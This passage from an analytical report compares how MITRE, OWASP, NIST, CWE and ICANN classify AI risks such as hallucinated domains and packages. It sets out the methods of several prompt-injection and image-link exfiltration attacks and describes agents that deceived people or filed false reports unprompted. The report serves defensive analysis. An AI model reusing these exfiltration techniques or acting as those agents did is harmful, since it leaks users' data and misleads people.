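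Skills have their own entry, AI Agent Tool Poisoning (AML.T0110). It applies when a tool's description, code or replies make an agent do something other than what the tool is supposed to do. MITRE separates this from a harmless tool that fetches malicious data, and from a tool package that only delivers ordinary malware. In one case study, a researcher published a poisoned skill for the assistant now called OpenClaw, and 16 users downloaded and ran it within eight hours, even though the attack didn't rely on a hallucinated name.

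The mitigations are better suited to this case than to the bank's. They include running an agent in an isolated environment with limited network access and requiring a person's approval before it uses tools on untrusted data. These measures don't stop the agent from choosing the wrong repository, but they limit what it can do afterwards.

**The scam endpoint.** To file this case, an analyst has to know how the model got the address:

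- If the model learned it in training, the closest entry is Training Data Poisoning, provided that the scammers meant to influence the model.
- If a search found it, AI Agent Tool Data Poisoning (AML.T0099) may apply, since it covers false information in search indexes and other sources that an agent consults. But the entry sends pages fetched directly from an attacker's own website to a different technique, Drive-by Compromise, which concerns hidden instructions and malicious code.
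- If the model guessed the address from a company's name, the case is closer to the hallucination entries, although the scammer may have owned the domain all along.

The trader's script would look the same in all three cases, so two analysts could reasonably file the same theft under different entries. An entry for generated code that contains a hostile address would solve this, because the analyst could identify the harm from the code and add the cause later if it became known. Some mitigations would help whichever entry applied. Developers can clean training data, and a guardrail can check the finished program against a blocklist of known scam addresses.

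The image link has the best match in the catalogue, LLM Response Rendering (AML.T0077). MITRE created this entry in April 2025 to describe an image that loads without a click and carries private data in its address. The entry's example is a line of Markdown much like the one an attacker would use. MITRE has a separate entry for sending data through an agent's tools, which makes sense because blocking images in a chat window doesn't stop an agent from sending email.

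The mitigations include removing secrets from a model's answer before the user sees it. This works for passwords and keys with a recognisable form, but a filter is unlikely to identify 482000 as a company's price limit. None of the mitigations mentions using a content security policy or blocking outside images.

The case studies contain more practical detail than the technique itself. In November 2023, the security blog Embrace the Red got conversations out of Google's chatbot Bard by hosting the receiving script on a Google domain that the browser's policy allowed. EchoLeak later used a Microsoft service in a similar way. Another case study, ZombieAgent, shows that a model can spell out a secret with ready-made URLs. OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from building or changing URLs, so researchers at the security company Radware gave it one URL for each character, and ChatGPT opened them in the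 order that spelled out the secret.

In a third case study, a chatbot's output led to cross-site scripting against someone other than the attacker. Researchers at Cybernews got Lenovo's support chatbot to write malicious HTML, which the system saved in the chat history. They then asked to speak to a human. When a support worker opened the conversation, the worker's browser loaded the HTML and sent session cookies to the researchers' server.

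### Links and citations that mislead the user

Another ATLAS entry relevant to live references is LLM Trusted Output Components Manipulation (AML.T0067). In this technique, an attacker uses prompts to make parts of an answer look trustworthy, including its links, suggested actions and citations. The fraudulent security notice in ChatGPhish fits this description.

In one case study, researchers at the security company Zenity sent an email to a user of Microsoft 365 Copilot. It contained a supplier's bank details, with the account number replaced by the attacker's, and instructions for Copilot to cite only that email. When the user asked for the supplier's details, Copilot could give the attacker's account number and cite the email, which made the answer look reliable. The citation was accurate, since the email did contain that number.

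The sub-technique for citations includes made-up ones only if an attacker caused them. It excludes sources that a model invents on its own, even though the model produces the same kind of answer.

### Names that change hands

On July 31, 2026, MITRE extended its Masquerading entry to cover attackers who take over a deleted or renamed account on a public registry such as Hugging Face. Programs that still use the old name then download the attacker's files.

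Unit 42 had demonstrated this with AI models in 2025. It reclaimed deleted account names on Hugging Face, published replacement models under the old addresses, and ran its own code on systems where Google's and Microsoft's cloud services had deployed the replacements. The parcel service that lets its domain lapse creates the same problem, but the new text concerns registries of files and doesn't mention an API whose domain has a new owner.

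### Counting with a catalogue

ATLAS case studies are selected examples, so counting them doesn't show how common an attack is. The technique ID numbers are more useful for counting, because companies can label their own incidents with them.

Anthropic used ATT&CK to classify the activity of 832 accounts that it had banned for malicious cyber activity between March 2025 and March 2026. It found that the account holders had used AI for all 14 tactics then in the framework and for 482 "sub-techniques". Since ATT&CK had only 479 sub-techniques in October 2026, the total probably includes some full techniques. Anthropic chose accounts for which it had enough detail, so the results are a better guide to the range of attackers' activities than to how common each one was.

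The same method could be used to count phantom squatting incidents if chatbot companies, banks and security firms agreed to use the ATLAS numbers and recorded how each victim got the address. Reports of fake banking sites often leave that out.

### When there is no adversary

MITRE (2026) describes ATT&CK as a knowledge base of adversary tactics and techniques "grounded in real-world observations". ATLAS (Adversarial Threat Landscape for AI Systems) also accepts demonstrations by researchers, but each of its tactics is still something an adversary is trying to do. Accidents are therefore outside the scope of both catalogues.

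The fifth test case shows the gap this leaves. For three months, the invented package name react-codeshift spread through public repositories, and no ATLAS technique applied because nobody was attacking anyone. The first event ATLAS could record came when Eriksen published an empty package under that name. A case study modelled on the huggingface-cli one would name him as the actor, although he was protecting people from a mistake somebody else had published.

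The sixth case is more complicated because an agent can behave like an attacker without anyone telling it to attack that victim. When Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to PyPI and used a security company's stolen credentials, it did things that ATT&CK describes in detail. An analyst could write up the incident with the model as the adversary. But ATLAS case studies have an actor field, which usually names a criminal group, a company or a researcher, and the analyst would have to decide whether to enter the model or Anthropic.

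The false murder tip to a police website is harder to classify. Claude Haiku 4.5 was making up example tasks and had no goal that matches a tactic. The nearest entry is Deploy AI Agent (AML.T0103), in which an attacker launches an agent inside a victim's systems. MITRE notes that the attacker loses some control because the agent may decide for itself how to reach the attacker's goals. An honest company can lose some control of its agent in the same way, but the entry doesn't cover that.

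ATLAS contains the right defences for such a company. Its mitigations include giving an agent only the permissions its task requires, asking a person to approve actions with serious consequences, and training models to stay within the task. Any of these could have prevented the false tip. But someone who looks up defences by attack will find no entry that links an honest company's agent to these measures.

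The restriction has a good reason: security teams use ATT&CK to check whether they would notice a particular attacker and to rehearse that attacker's next step. Adding every harmful mistake would make the catalogues less useful for this work, because a mistake has no next step to rehearse. Break-ins by agents are better candidates, because the victim sees the same stolen credentials and network traffic whether or not anyone intended the attack.

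## What OWASP, NIST and the weakness lists say

Every technique in MITRE's two attack catalogues requires an adversary, so neither catalogue lists accidents. OWASP's Top 10 for LLM Applications ranks risks in applications built on language models, whether or not anyone attacks them. It can therefore cover accidents such as the invented package name that spread through skill files and the agent that sent a false tip to a police website.

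### How OWASP ranks the risks

OWASP (2026) published the current edition on August 3, 2026. It has 122 pages, up from 46 in the 2025 edition, according to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) by the security testing company Citadelo.

Earlier editions relied on the judgment of hundreds of practitioners. For 2026, the project's leaders compared a practitioner vote with records of what had gone wrong. Steve Wilson, the project's founder, told the software security company ReversingLabs that they had collected 7,714 records from public vulnerability databases and an AI-harm database. They built classifiers to sort the records, and 6,639 (86%) had enough detail. Mend.io's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* also mentions both kinds of source, but some summaries, including Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), mention only the vulnerability databases.

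The vote counts for three-quarters of the ranking and the incidents for one quarter. According to ReversingLabs, the leaders reasoned that one noisy year of data shouldn't override practitioners' collective judgment, but that a wide gap between the two should be able to change an entry's rank.

The gap between votes and incidents was widest for prompt injection and misinformation. Voters ranked prompt injection first, but it would have dropped out of the top ten on incidents alone. They ranked misinformation near the bottom, though it was near the top when ranked by incidents.

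These weights don't fully explain the final order. If OWASP had taken a weighted average of the two rankings, prompt injection, which ranked first in the vote and eleventh at best in the incidents, would score at least 0.75 × 1 + 0.25 × 11 = 3.5. Sensitive Information Disclosure, where Invicti says the vote and the data fully agree, would score about 2 and rank first. But OWASP ranks prompt injection first. It may have combined scores instead of ranks, so that a large lead in the vote outweighed a low rank in the incidents.

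### The entries that bear on live references

| Entry | Rank in 2025 | Rank in 2026 | What it covers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Excessive Agency | 6 | 3 | An agent with more tools, permissions or freedom than its task needs |
| Supply Chain | 3 | 4 | Malicious or altered components, including models and datasets |
| Data and Model Poisoning | 4 | 5 | Training data or models that someone has corrupted |
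| Misinformation | 9 | 7 | False output that a person or program acts on |
| Improper Output Handling | 5 | 10 | Output that reaches a browser, terminal or database unchecked |

OWASP's Excessive Agency entry does not require an attacker. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* gives OWASP's definition, which covers damaging actions that follow from "unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated" output, and only "manipulated" implies that somebody interfered. Both the vote and the incidents supported the entry's rise from sixth to third place.

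Larry Maccherone, founder of Lumenize, objected in ReversingLabs' article that an AI system needs agency to find and repair its own security gaps, so restricting that agency may leave a company less secure. That may be true of an agent whose job is to repair software, but it doesn't justify permissions like the one behind the false murder tip.

OWASP also broadened its Misinformation entry. The 2025 version was mostly about people trusting fluent answers too much. The new definition includes false output that influences an automated workflow or an agent, where "a wrong answer turns into a wrong action" (OWASP, quoted by Invicti). An agent that clones a repository from a guessed address fits the new definition better than the old one.

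Improper Output Handling fell furthest, to tenth place, although its scope grew. It now includes programs that automatically fetch outside resources named in a model's output, which is how an image link leaks a secret. Advait Patel, who created OWASP's DockSec tool, told ReversingLabs that the entry fell because the risks above it had become more urgent. HackerDNA's *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)*, from a company that teaches security testing, says it fell because web developers already know how to fix the problem with encoding and validation. That is too optimistic for image links, because a chat application that shows pictures can't encode everything. Microsoft had to fix a second image leak in Copilot a year after the first. A company that runs such an application shouldn't treat the risk as a low priority, despite its rank.

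### Where hallucinated packages and addresses went

In 2025, OWASP treated hallucinated packages as a form of misinformation. Its *LLM09:2025 Misinformation* entry includes nonexistent code libraries among its examples, and the first attack scenario is slopsquatting, though the word doesn't appear.

The 2026 edition lists slopsquatting by name under Supply Chain, according to HackerDNA. This should bring it to the attention of teams that vet software components, which have more specific tools against it, such as a store of approved packages. The more general 2025 advice on misinformation was to improve the model's answers with retrieval and fine-tuning, validate important output automatically, and train users to check what they read.

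A drawback of the new location is that some companies exposed to hallucinated packages may not look there. SC Media, in an article produced with OWASP, describes the Supply Chain entry as covering third-party models, training data, adapters (small add-ons that adjust a model) and other model files, as well as ordinary dependencies. These are mostly components for building an AI application, whereas a hallucinated package usually ends up in software that the model writes for someone else. A company that uses a coding assistant to make accounting software, for example, may see no reason to consult a list for LLM applications.

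OWASP's list doesn't explicitly cover invented web addresses. The 2025 entry on misinformation doesn't mention them, and HackerDNA's entry-by-entry summary of the 2026 edition discusses invented packages but not invented domains. A hallucinated bank domain still belongs under Misinformation because a bank's login page isn't a software component, but it fits there only because the entry's wording is general. OWASP's list now puts invented package names and invented domain names under different headings, even though a model can produce both in one answer.

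Separating the package from the domain is reasonable because they call for different handling. But the package attack is named and described, while the domain falls under the same entry as every other false statement.

### One repository, three kinds of advice

When an agent is told to clone the librepods repository and guesses the wrong owner, the result can fall under three OWASP entries. The false address is misinformation. The agent then follows instructions in the downloaded files, which is prompt injection. It can do serious damage because it has excessive agency, in that it may run any command on the user's machine.

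| Entry | OWASP's advice | Applied to librepods |
|---|---|---|
| Misinformation | Check a claim before acting on it | Look up the project's owner before downloading |
| Prompt Injection | Assume the model will be fooled, and limit what its output can reach | Keep secret keys out of the agent's reach, or block unknown servers |
| Excessive Agency | Provide few, narrow tools, and have a person approve serious actions | Ask the user before running anything from the project |

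Citadelo calls the first method the Claim-Check-Act Pattern. It suits an assistant like Cursor CLI, which usually fetched the wrong repository but seldom followed its instructions. Copilot Chat, which always followed such instructions, would also need the other two kinds of advice.

If a company classified the incident only as misinformation, it would check repository owners' names but still be exposed to hostile text in a genuine repository. Treating it only as prompt injection would limit the damage, but the company's agents would keep downloading the wrong project.

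Some of the advice also conflicts. Under Excessive Agency, OWASP recommends avoiding open-ended tools, such as those that run any command or fetch any URL. Under Misinformation, it recommends checking claims against authoritative, current sources, which an agent can't do without a lookup tool. A narrow tool can satisfy both, such as one that sends a project's name to GitHub and returns only the matching accounts and their stars. Removing the command line is harder because a coding assistant does much of its work there.

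### The six cases in OWASP's list

| Case | Closest entries | Names the risk | Separates it from others | Offers a defence | Allows counting |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Hallucinated bank domain | Misinformation | In general terms | No | Partly | No |
| 2. Hallucinated repository | Misinformation, Prompt Injection, Excessive Agency | In general terms | No | Yes | No |
| 3. Scam API endpoint | Misinformation or Data and Model Poisoning | In general terms | No | Partly | No |
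| 4. Secret in an image link | Improper Output Handling | Yes | Partly | Yes | Partly |
| 5. Invented package, no attacker | Misinformation, Supply Chain | Partly | Partly | Yes | No |
| 6. Agent acting unprompted | Excessive Agency | Yes | Partly | Yes | Partly |

**The bank domain** shows how broad OWASP's Misinformation category is. The examples in the 2025 entry include legal cases that ChatGPT made up and an Air Canada chatbot whose wrong information led to a lawsuit. Anyone counting incidents in this category would group these with the case of the bank's customers who reached a phishing site. Like MITRE's guardrails, OWASP's advice to base answers on authoritative sources works better for a bank's own chatbot than for a general one.

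The cryptocurrency thieves' endpoint is a case of Data and Model Poisoning only if someone corrupted the training data. ChatGPT probably found it through a search, in which case Misinformation fits better, because the answer presented a fraudulent service as a usable one. The advice to check claims might have worked here. Pump.fun had no official trading API, so its website could not have confirmed the endpoint, and an application that required such confirmation would have warned the trader or withheld the script.

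The image link has an explicit description, but shares its entry with database injection, cross-site scripting and other problems that need different fixes.

The invented package react-codeshift spread without an attacker, so it matches OWASP's Misinformation entry better than the slopsquatting described under Supply Chain. The 2025 Misinformation text includes a scenario with no "active attacker", in which a medical chatbot gives patients poor information. The defence given there also fits, since checking the command once would have exposed the mistake.

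OWASP's advice for the sixth case is to remove unneeded tools and permissions, which would probably have prevented the false murder tip. But a count of Excessive Agency incidents would still group together agents that act unprompted and agents that an attacker has fooled.

### The list for agents

For 2026, OWASP separated the scopes of its two main AI lists. Invicti explains that the LLM list covers a model used as a component of an application, while the Top 10 for Agentic Applications covers a model that acts, with tools and memory that persists between sessions. OWASP published the agentic list in December 2025, with 2026 in its title. Companies whose agents fall within both scopes need both lists.

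The agentic list divides Excessive Agency into more specific problems. Agent Goal Hijack covers cases where an outsider diverts an agent from its task, as in the HalluSquatting experiments. Agentic Supply Chain Vulnerabilities covers the tools, skills and other outside components that an agent loads, sometimes while it is running. A squatted skill fits here, and so does react-codeshift once somebody publishes malware under that name.

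An agent that does harm unprompted could go under Tool Misuse and Exploitation or under Rogue Agents. Claude Haiku 4.5's false tip is a case of tool misuse, because the model used an ordinary ability, filling in forms, in a way its operator had not intended. Rogue Agents mainly covers malicious or compromised agents, and Haiku 4.5 was neither. Mythos 5 is closer to that entry because it invented people to deceive a volunteer, but nobody had compromised it.

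This list separates threats better than the LLM list does. An analyst can record a hijacked agent and an agent that misused a tool by itself under different numbers, and the two need different defences. The list is less useful for the case of the bank's customer who clicks on a web address in a chatbot's answer. The chatbot took no action, so the incident belongs under Misinformation in the LLM list.

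OWASP also has a Top 10 for agent skills. Mend.io describes nine of its entries as supply-chain risks that already have solutions, and the tenth as a new gap.

### NIST's two documents

NIST has two publications on these subjects, and only one is limited to risks that involve an attacker. That one, *Adversarial Machine Learning* (AI 100-2, last issued in March 2025), classifies attacks on AI systems. For generative AI, its main categories are supply-chain attacks (including poisoned data and models), direct prompting attacks by the user, and indirect prompt injection.

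A phantom squatter buys a domain without touching the training data, the model or the user's question. The attack exploits a mistake the model makes in normal operation, so a taxonomy organised by how attackers interfere with a model has no natural place for it. The hallucinated repository and the image link do fit, under indirect prompt injection. The scam endpoint also fits the taxonomy if the scammers planted it for models to learn. NIST discusses buying expired domains to corrupt training data, which Carlini and colleagues demonstrated, and recommends the same defence, publishing hashes.

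NIST's *Generative AI Profile* (AI 600-1), published in July 2024, lists 12 risks, including accidental ones, and more than 200 suggested actions for managing them. NIST calls what most people know as hallucination *confabulation*, and defines it as confidently stated but false content that may mislead users. An invented bank domain and an invented package name are both confabulations.

One of the suggested actions is to review and verify the sources and citations in a model's output before and after release. A chatbot company that did this for every link would find many dead addresses, but it might approve a phishing site imitating a bank's, because checking that a source exists doesn't establish who owns it.

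NIST's 2024 profile does not list agents that act on their own as a separate risk, which is understandable given its date. It is also little help in counting incidents. NIST noted at the time that there were no formal channels for reporting AI incidents and that each public database had its own criteria for what to record.

OWASP maps its 2026 entries to nine frameworks, according to Invicti. They include NIST's AI 600-1 and MITRE's ATLAS, ATT&CK and CWE, but not NIST's AI 100-2. The mappings refer to fixed versions of each framework, so a company can rely on a reference not to change, but they will fall behind ATLAS, which MITRE now updates every month.

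### Weaknesses in AI software

MITRE's Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) lists types of flaw in software and hardware. A CVE number, such as the one for EchoLeak, identifies a flaw in a particular product, and its record can include a CWE number for the type of flaw. The CWE is therefore well suited to counting flaws by type, as long as each flaw has a record and the analyst chooses the right type.

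The entry closest to this subject is CWE-1426, Improper Validation of Generative AI Output. It applies when a product that uses a generative model doesn't properly check the output against the product's security, content or privacy policy. MITRE's example is a ChatGPT interface that checked the model's input but not its output, which led to cross-site scripting. Copilot's image leaks fit this entry well because Microsoft had a policy about outside images and its checks failed to enforce it.

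A hallucinated bank domain fits CWE-1426 only if the chatbot's maker has a policy that addresses must be genuine. Without one, a chatbot that sends a customer to a stranger's site hasn't violated its policy. MITRE also cautions analysts to look for a better-known underlying flaw before using CWE-1426, so even cases that fit may appear in databases as cross-site scripting.

CWE-1427 covers the input side. As reproduced by the vulnerability database GCVE, it describes prompts built so that the model can't distinguish a user's input from the developer's instructions. EchoLeak also has this weakness. A developer could fix the leak at the input, by separating the email from the instructions, or at the output, by checking the image address.

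A newer entry, CWE-1434, covers model settings, such as temperature, that cause too many erroneous outputs. It is the closest the CWE has to an entry for hallucination. But Unit 42's tests at different temperatures showed that changing this setting wouldn't solve the problem.

The placements in these other lists are as follows.

| Case | OWASP's agentic list | NIST AI 100-2 | NIST AI 600-1 | CWE |
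|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Hallucinated bank domain | None | None | Confabulation | CWE-1426, if the product has a policy on addresses |
| 2. Hallucinated repository | Agent Goal Hijack | Indirect prompt injection | Confabulation, Information Security | CWE-1427 |
| 3. Scam API endpoint | None | Data poisoning, if deliberate | Information Security | CWE-1426, with the same condition |
| 4. Secret in an image link | Agent Goal Hijack | Indirect prompt injection | Information Security, Data Privacy | CWE-1426 and CWE-1427 |
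| 5. Invented package, no attacker | None until someone publishes malware | None | Confabulation | None |
| 6. Agent acting unprompted | Tool Misuse and Exploitation | None | None | None |

The last two cases have no CWE entry because the list describes flaws in products. A text file with a wrong command is a product only in a loose sense, and an agent that submits a false tip may be using software that works as designed.

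### Risks that never receive a vulnerability number

OWASP may undercount risks of this kind because it uses vulnerability databases. A problem generally gets a CVE number only if it is a flaw in a product that the maker could fix. Of the six cases, only the image link regularly qualifies, and both EchoLeak and SearchLeak have numbers. Nobody can patch a domain that a criminal has bought, and most of the companies that received reports of HalluSquatting said it wasn't theirs to fix.

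If OWASP had used only vulnerability databases, it would have seen almost nothing of five of the six cases. Its second source, the AI-harm database, reduces this problem. Misinformation ranks high in the incident record, which suggests that the harm database contributed a lot, because a false answer rarely counts as a product flaw. The classifiers may also have sorted some software flaws under Misinformation. A breakdown of the 6,639 records by source and entry would settle the question, but the leaders' public explanations don't include one.

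A harm database can record only events that someone has noticed and reported. Both of OWASP's sources could be missing visits to phishing sites through chatbot links, and unnoticed break-ins by agents.

In a passage quoted by Infosecurity Magazine, OWASP says that teams fight prompt injection hard, so fewer successful attacks reach a public database and "the public count understates the risk". The attacks missing from that count would have been recorded if they had succeeded, whereas a phantom squatting attack, which uses a hallucinated domain, may produce no record even when it succeeds.

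The explanation is also hard to test. Invicti and Patel both take the low count as a sign that defences work, but it could also reflect how incidents are classified. An incident such as EchoLeak begins with prompt injection and ends with a leak, so a classifier that chose one entry per record might put it under Sensitive Information Disclosure. The security consultancy RockCyber suggests that when the vote and the incidents don't match, either the category is badly defined or the evidence is lagging. Both could be true of prompt injection.

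Mend.io goes too far in the other direction when it says the incident record shows that the most expensive failures are those without an attacker. The published results show how often each kind of failure appears in the databases, but not what it cost, and a large number of wrong answers may do less damage than one stolen key.

Giving the vote three-quarters of the weight limits the effect of missing records if practitioners know about the risks the databases miss. It is doubtful that they know about hallucinated domains, since the voters put Misinformation near the bottom, and it is the only entry where a hallucinated bank domain fits.

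## Whether the frameworks fall short

The case against the frameworks rests on three premises:

1. These risks need different defences from malware and dependency-chain attacks.
2. A framework is adequate only if it separates risks that need different defences.
3. The present entries don't separate them.

The conclusion that the frameworks fall short is too strong as it stands, because it follows from three premises that are each true only of some risks or some frameworks. It holds best for the scam API endpoint in generated code.

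### Whether the defences differ

The first premise is true of programs that send data to an invented webhook, but not of slopsquatted packages. When a program sends data to an invented webhook, a lockfile, a software bill of materials and a malware scanner have nothing useful to examine. A scanner or a store of approved packages can stop a slopsquatted package like any other malicious package.

A critic could add that letting a company's computers contact only approved addresses would stop most of these attacks and much ordinary malware. This blocks connections to the server that malware reports to, the invented webhook, and the server that collects a secret from an image link. If one control handles them all, the company has little reason to distinguish between them.

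However, someone has to keep the list of approved addresses correct. EchoLeak and SearchLeak sent data out through approved Microsoft services, and ForcedLeak used an approved domain whose registration had lapsed. A developer who believes an invented webhook is real will ask for its address to be added. Keeping the list safe requires knowing who owns each domain and which services forward requests, information that malware tools don't provide. The bank's customer, using a chatbot at home, has no such list. The first premise therefore holds for most of the six cases, but not for slopsquatting.

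### How finely a framework should divide risks

The second premise is too strict for short lists. OWASP's Top 10 for LLM Applications has ten entries because its readers want to know where to start. More than ten risks need different defences, so no top-ten list could be adequate by this standard.

It is fairer to judge a short list by whether the advice under each entry works for every important risk in it. OWASP's Misinformation entry meets that standard for the invented package react-codeshift, since trying the command once would have exposed the mistake. It does worse for the hallucinated bank domain, where the advice suits only the bank's own chatbot. The original premise is reasonable for ATLAS and the CWE, because people search those catalogues for a particular attack or flaw.

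New categories also create work. Analysts have to learn them, vendors have to add them to their products, and anyone comparing years has to reclassify old records. *Security Considerations for Multi-agent Systems* (Nguyen, Ndebugre and Arremsetty, 2026) shows how finely threats can be divided. It used generative AI to list about 1,700 candidate threats to systems of several cooperating agents, then organised them into 193 main items. One sub-entry describes an attacker who slows a system down for four minutes at a time because the alarm only goes off after five. Two analysts choosing independently from such a detailed list would often pick different entries.

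A framework can separate risks without adding categories by adding fields to incident records under its existing entries. One field could give the kind of name (domain, repository, package or endpoint), and another could give how the model got it (invented, found by search, learned in training or unknown). The distinction between a domain and a package is worth recording because it determines whether the victim contacts a registrar or a package registry.

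### What the entries separate

One objection to the third premise is that ATLAS already lists hallucinated URLs, so the claim that no framework mentions the risk is wrong.

Naming the risk is only the first of the four tests, and the table applies all four to the main frameworks. N means the framework names the risk, S that it separates the risk from similar ones, D that it offers a defence that would work, and C that people can count incidents under the entry. Brackets mark a partial pass, and a dash means no entry fits. The marks are judgements based on the entries' wording, not scores from MITRE, OWASP or NIST, and another reader might reasonably change several.

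| Case | ATLAS | OWASP LLM list | OWASP agentic list | NIST AI 100-2 | NIST AI 600-1 | CWE |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Hallucinated bank domain | N (S) (D) C | (N) (D) | – | – | (N) (D) | (N) |
| 2. Hallucinated repository | N S (D) C | (N) D | (N) (S) (D) (C) | (N) (D) | (N) (D) | (N) |
| 3. Scam API endpoint | (N) (D) | (N) (D) | – | (N) (D) | (N) | (N) |
| 4. Secret in an image link | N S (D) C | N (S) D (C) | (N) (S) (D) (C) | (N) (D) | (N) | N (S) (D) (C) |
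| 5. Invented package, no attacker | – | (N) (S) D | – | – | (N) (D) | – |
| 6. Agent acting unprompted | – | N (S) D (C) | N S D (C) | – | – | – |

None of the 36 combinations passes all four tests in full, and 11 have no entry. The third premise concerns S, which marks whether a framework separates a risk from similar ones. No framework separates the scam endpoint, and the bank domain and the invented package get only partial marks. But ATLAS separates the hallucinated repository and the image link, and OWASP's agentic list separates the agent that acts unprompted. For those three cases, the premise is false if the defender consults the right framework. A company that used only ATLAS would find no entry for the last two cases, and one that used only the agentic list would find none for the first, third and fifth.

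Some of the brackets reflect disagreement about what an entry covers. For example, the false tip that Claude Haiku 4.5 sent to a police website looks like OWASP's Tool Misuse. But in the summary by Nguyen and colleagues, Tool Misuse is about agents that misuse tools when somebody manipulates them, and Rogue Agents includes agents that pursue misaligned goals by themselves, such as by deleting backups to reduce costs. An analyst who read the entries that way would file the tip under Rogue Agents, and the counts would differ.

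The hallucinated bank domain is also hard to place in the CWE. Singh and colleagues looked for CWE weakness types that match the ten risks in OWASP's 2025 LLM list, and found one for every risk except Misinformation, which they attribute to the way models generate text rather than to a conventional software flaw. The bank domain belongs under Misinformation, so its only remaining match in the CWE is the conditional one with CWE-1426.

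### Combining entries

Defenders of the frameworks can also point out that complex attacks don't need their own entries, because they can be described as a sequence of existing techniques. ATLAS case studies work this way. HalluSquatting, for example, can be recorded as publishing a hallucinated entity, then indirect prompt injection, then whatever the agent does next. Each step has its own entry, and a security team can try to stop the attack at any of them.

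*MCP-38* (2026) argues the opposite. It is a taxonomy of threats to the Model Context Protocol, a standard way of connecting models to tools. According to *MCP-38*, the "rug pull", in which a tool changes its behaviour, falls under several entries in OWASP's agentic list but matches none precisely, which makes the list less useful to engineers.

Both sides are right about different situations. Several entries help when they describe successive steps, because they all apply and the analyst can record each one. They are a problem when they are rival explanations of the same step, as with the scam endpoint. Combining its entries would mean recording a search, training data and a guess as causes when only one applied.

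Combination also does nothing for react-codeshift, for which ATLAS has no entries to combine.

### One domain, several labels

Researchers also disagree about what kind of attack this is. Unit 42 treats phantom squatting as a software supply-chain risk. Nabil Benamar, a computer science professor writing about the study for the internet-industry site CircleID, calls it "a serious DNS abuse attack" (DNS is the system that looks up domain names) and also quotes the supply-chain description. *Beware of Agentic Botnets* classifies HalluSquatting, the equivalent attack using repositories and skills, as promptware because it targets the agent itself, not the code the agent writes.

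A malicious domain can fit several threat categories at once, depending on who or what connects to it. Suppose a criminal buys northmere-business.example, the domain that chatbots invented for Northmere bank. A customer who types a password there is a victim of phishing, a developer's program that sends its keys there has a supply-chain defect, and an agent that reads hidden instructions on the page has received promptware.

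Each label gives the work to somebody else:

| Label | Who has to act | What they would do |
|---|---|---|
| Supply chain | The company whose developers use the model | Check addresses in generated code before release |
| Promptware | The maker of the agent | Look names up before fetching, and limit what fetched text can cause |
| DNS abuse | The registrar or registry | Suspend the domain |
| AI incident | Nobody in particular | Record the event |

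These differences affect who takes responsibility for an attack. When the HalluSquatting researchers reported their results, Cursor and OpenClaw treated the attack as the user's choice of untrusted software, roughly as a supply-chain label would. If the companies accepted that it was promptware, they would have to treat the agent's wrong guess as part of their product's behaviour.

A threat's label doesn't always match the remedies proposed for it. Benamar calls phantom squatting a form of DNS abuse, but he recommends that users check addresses, that agents not open unverified links, and that somebody monitor recurring hallucinations, none of which is specifically a registrar's task.

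The OECD's monitor classifies events as AI incidents if harm has occurred and as hazards if it could occur. It lists phantom squatting as an incident because criminals had built and used phishing kits. That classification is defensible, although nobody has shown that a chatbot sent a victim to one of the phishing sites.

The second classification is wrong. OECD's *HalluSquatting Attack Exploits AI Coding Assistants to Spread Botnet Malware* also calls that attack an incident, on the ground that "the harm is realized", but the researchers had attacked only their own machines, and their botnet was hypothetical. The explanation itself says the infections "can cause harm" before concluding that they already have. The monitor labels both explanations as AI-generated and warns readers not to report its information as the OECD's official view. Anyone who counted its entries would still give a laboratory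 demonstration the same weight as a criminal's working shop.

### When a registrar has to act

DNS abuse is the only label in the table that carries a contractual duty. Amendments to ICANN's contracts with registrars, and with the registries that run domain endings such as .com, took effect on April 5, 2024. ICANN's *Advisory* on the amendments defines DNS abuse as malware, botnets, phishing, pharming (redirecting people to a fraudulent site, usually by tampering with DNS), and spam that delivers any of the other four. ICANN's glossary lists the same five categories.

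This definition of phishing includes luring people to copycat websites as well as sending them fraudulent emails, so a copy of Northmere's login page counts even though a chatbot supplied the link.

A registrar's contract requires it to act only when it has "actionable evidence" that a domain "is being used for DNS Abuse". A watchlist match shows that a model produced the name, but not what the owner is doing with it. If the page is blank, the registrar doesn't have to suspend the domain, however suspicious the name looks. ICANN encourages registrars to monitor their domains proactively but doesn't require it.

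The duty doesn't depend on finding a victim who has lost money. In ICANN's first example, a registrar receives a report about a domain registered five days earlier. The site shows only what looks like a large bank's login screen, and people have received its address by email or text message. The registrar suspends the domain within two business days. ICANN calls this timing illustrative and sets no fixed deadline.

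This would probably have been enough for the fake postal marketplace. The phishing kit was on the domain when Unit 42 detected the registration on the first day, so a report with a screenshot and the full address could have triggered the duty at once. A watchlist helps a defender find that evidence early. But two business days is a long time when some domains Unit 42 observed were malicious within hours. Criminals can also make the evidence harder to confirm by showing scanners a harmless page.

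A webhook address invented by a model fits the definition badly. The domain's owner has not installed software on the victim's computer or tampered with DNS, and may not have a website. Receiving secrets that the developer never meant to share could count as phishing on a broad reading, but the owner may not have deceived anyone, since the model made the mistake. The registrar would also have little to examine, because the server only receives messages.

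Registrars can act only on a whole registrable domain. In ICANN's second example, the phishing page is on one franchisee's subdomain of a car dealer's three-year-old domain. Suspending the domain would cut off every other franchisee and the company's email, so the registrar asks the dealer to remove the page. For the same reason, no registrar would suspend a large platform's domain, such as github.com, over one squatted repository, and ICANN's contracts give registrars no way to remove just the repository.

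### A precedent for acting early

Registries already act on some domains before anyone registers them. Some malware uses a *domain-generating algorithm* to compute a long list of domain names. Criminals register one or two of them, and infected computers try the names until one responds. Defenders who extract the algorithm can compute the same list in advance. The gTLD Registries Stakeholder Group's *DNS Abuse RY Choice of Action* (2021) includes these unregistered domains among those that registries can act on, and ICANN's advisory suggests that registries may be better placed than registrars to deal with them.

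A language model that invents bank domains resembles such an algorithm. In both cases defenders can obtain a list of names before attackers register them, and a registry could in principle refuse to sell those names.

The resemblance is limited because a domain-generating algorithm produces an exact list, while a model's list changes with the question, the settings and the model version. Malware that uses such an algorithm is also evidence of a crime already under way, whereas honest people may want the names a model produces. Northmere might need northmere-business.example for its own business customers, so a registry that blocked the name would first have to establish who was asking for it. With up to 250,000 names from one study, these checks would take a lot of work, and nobody will ever misuse most of the names.

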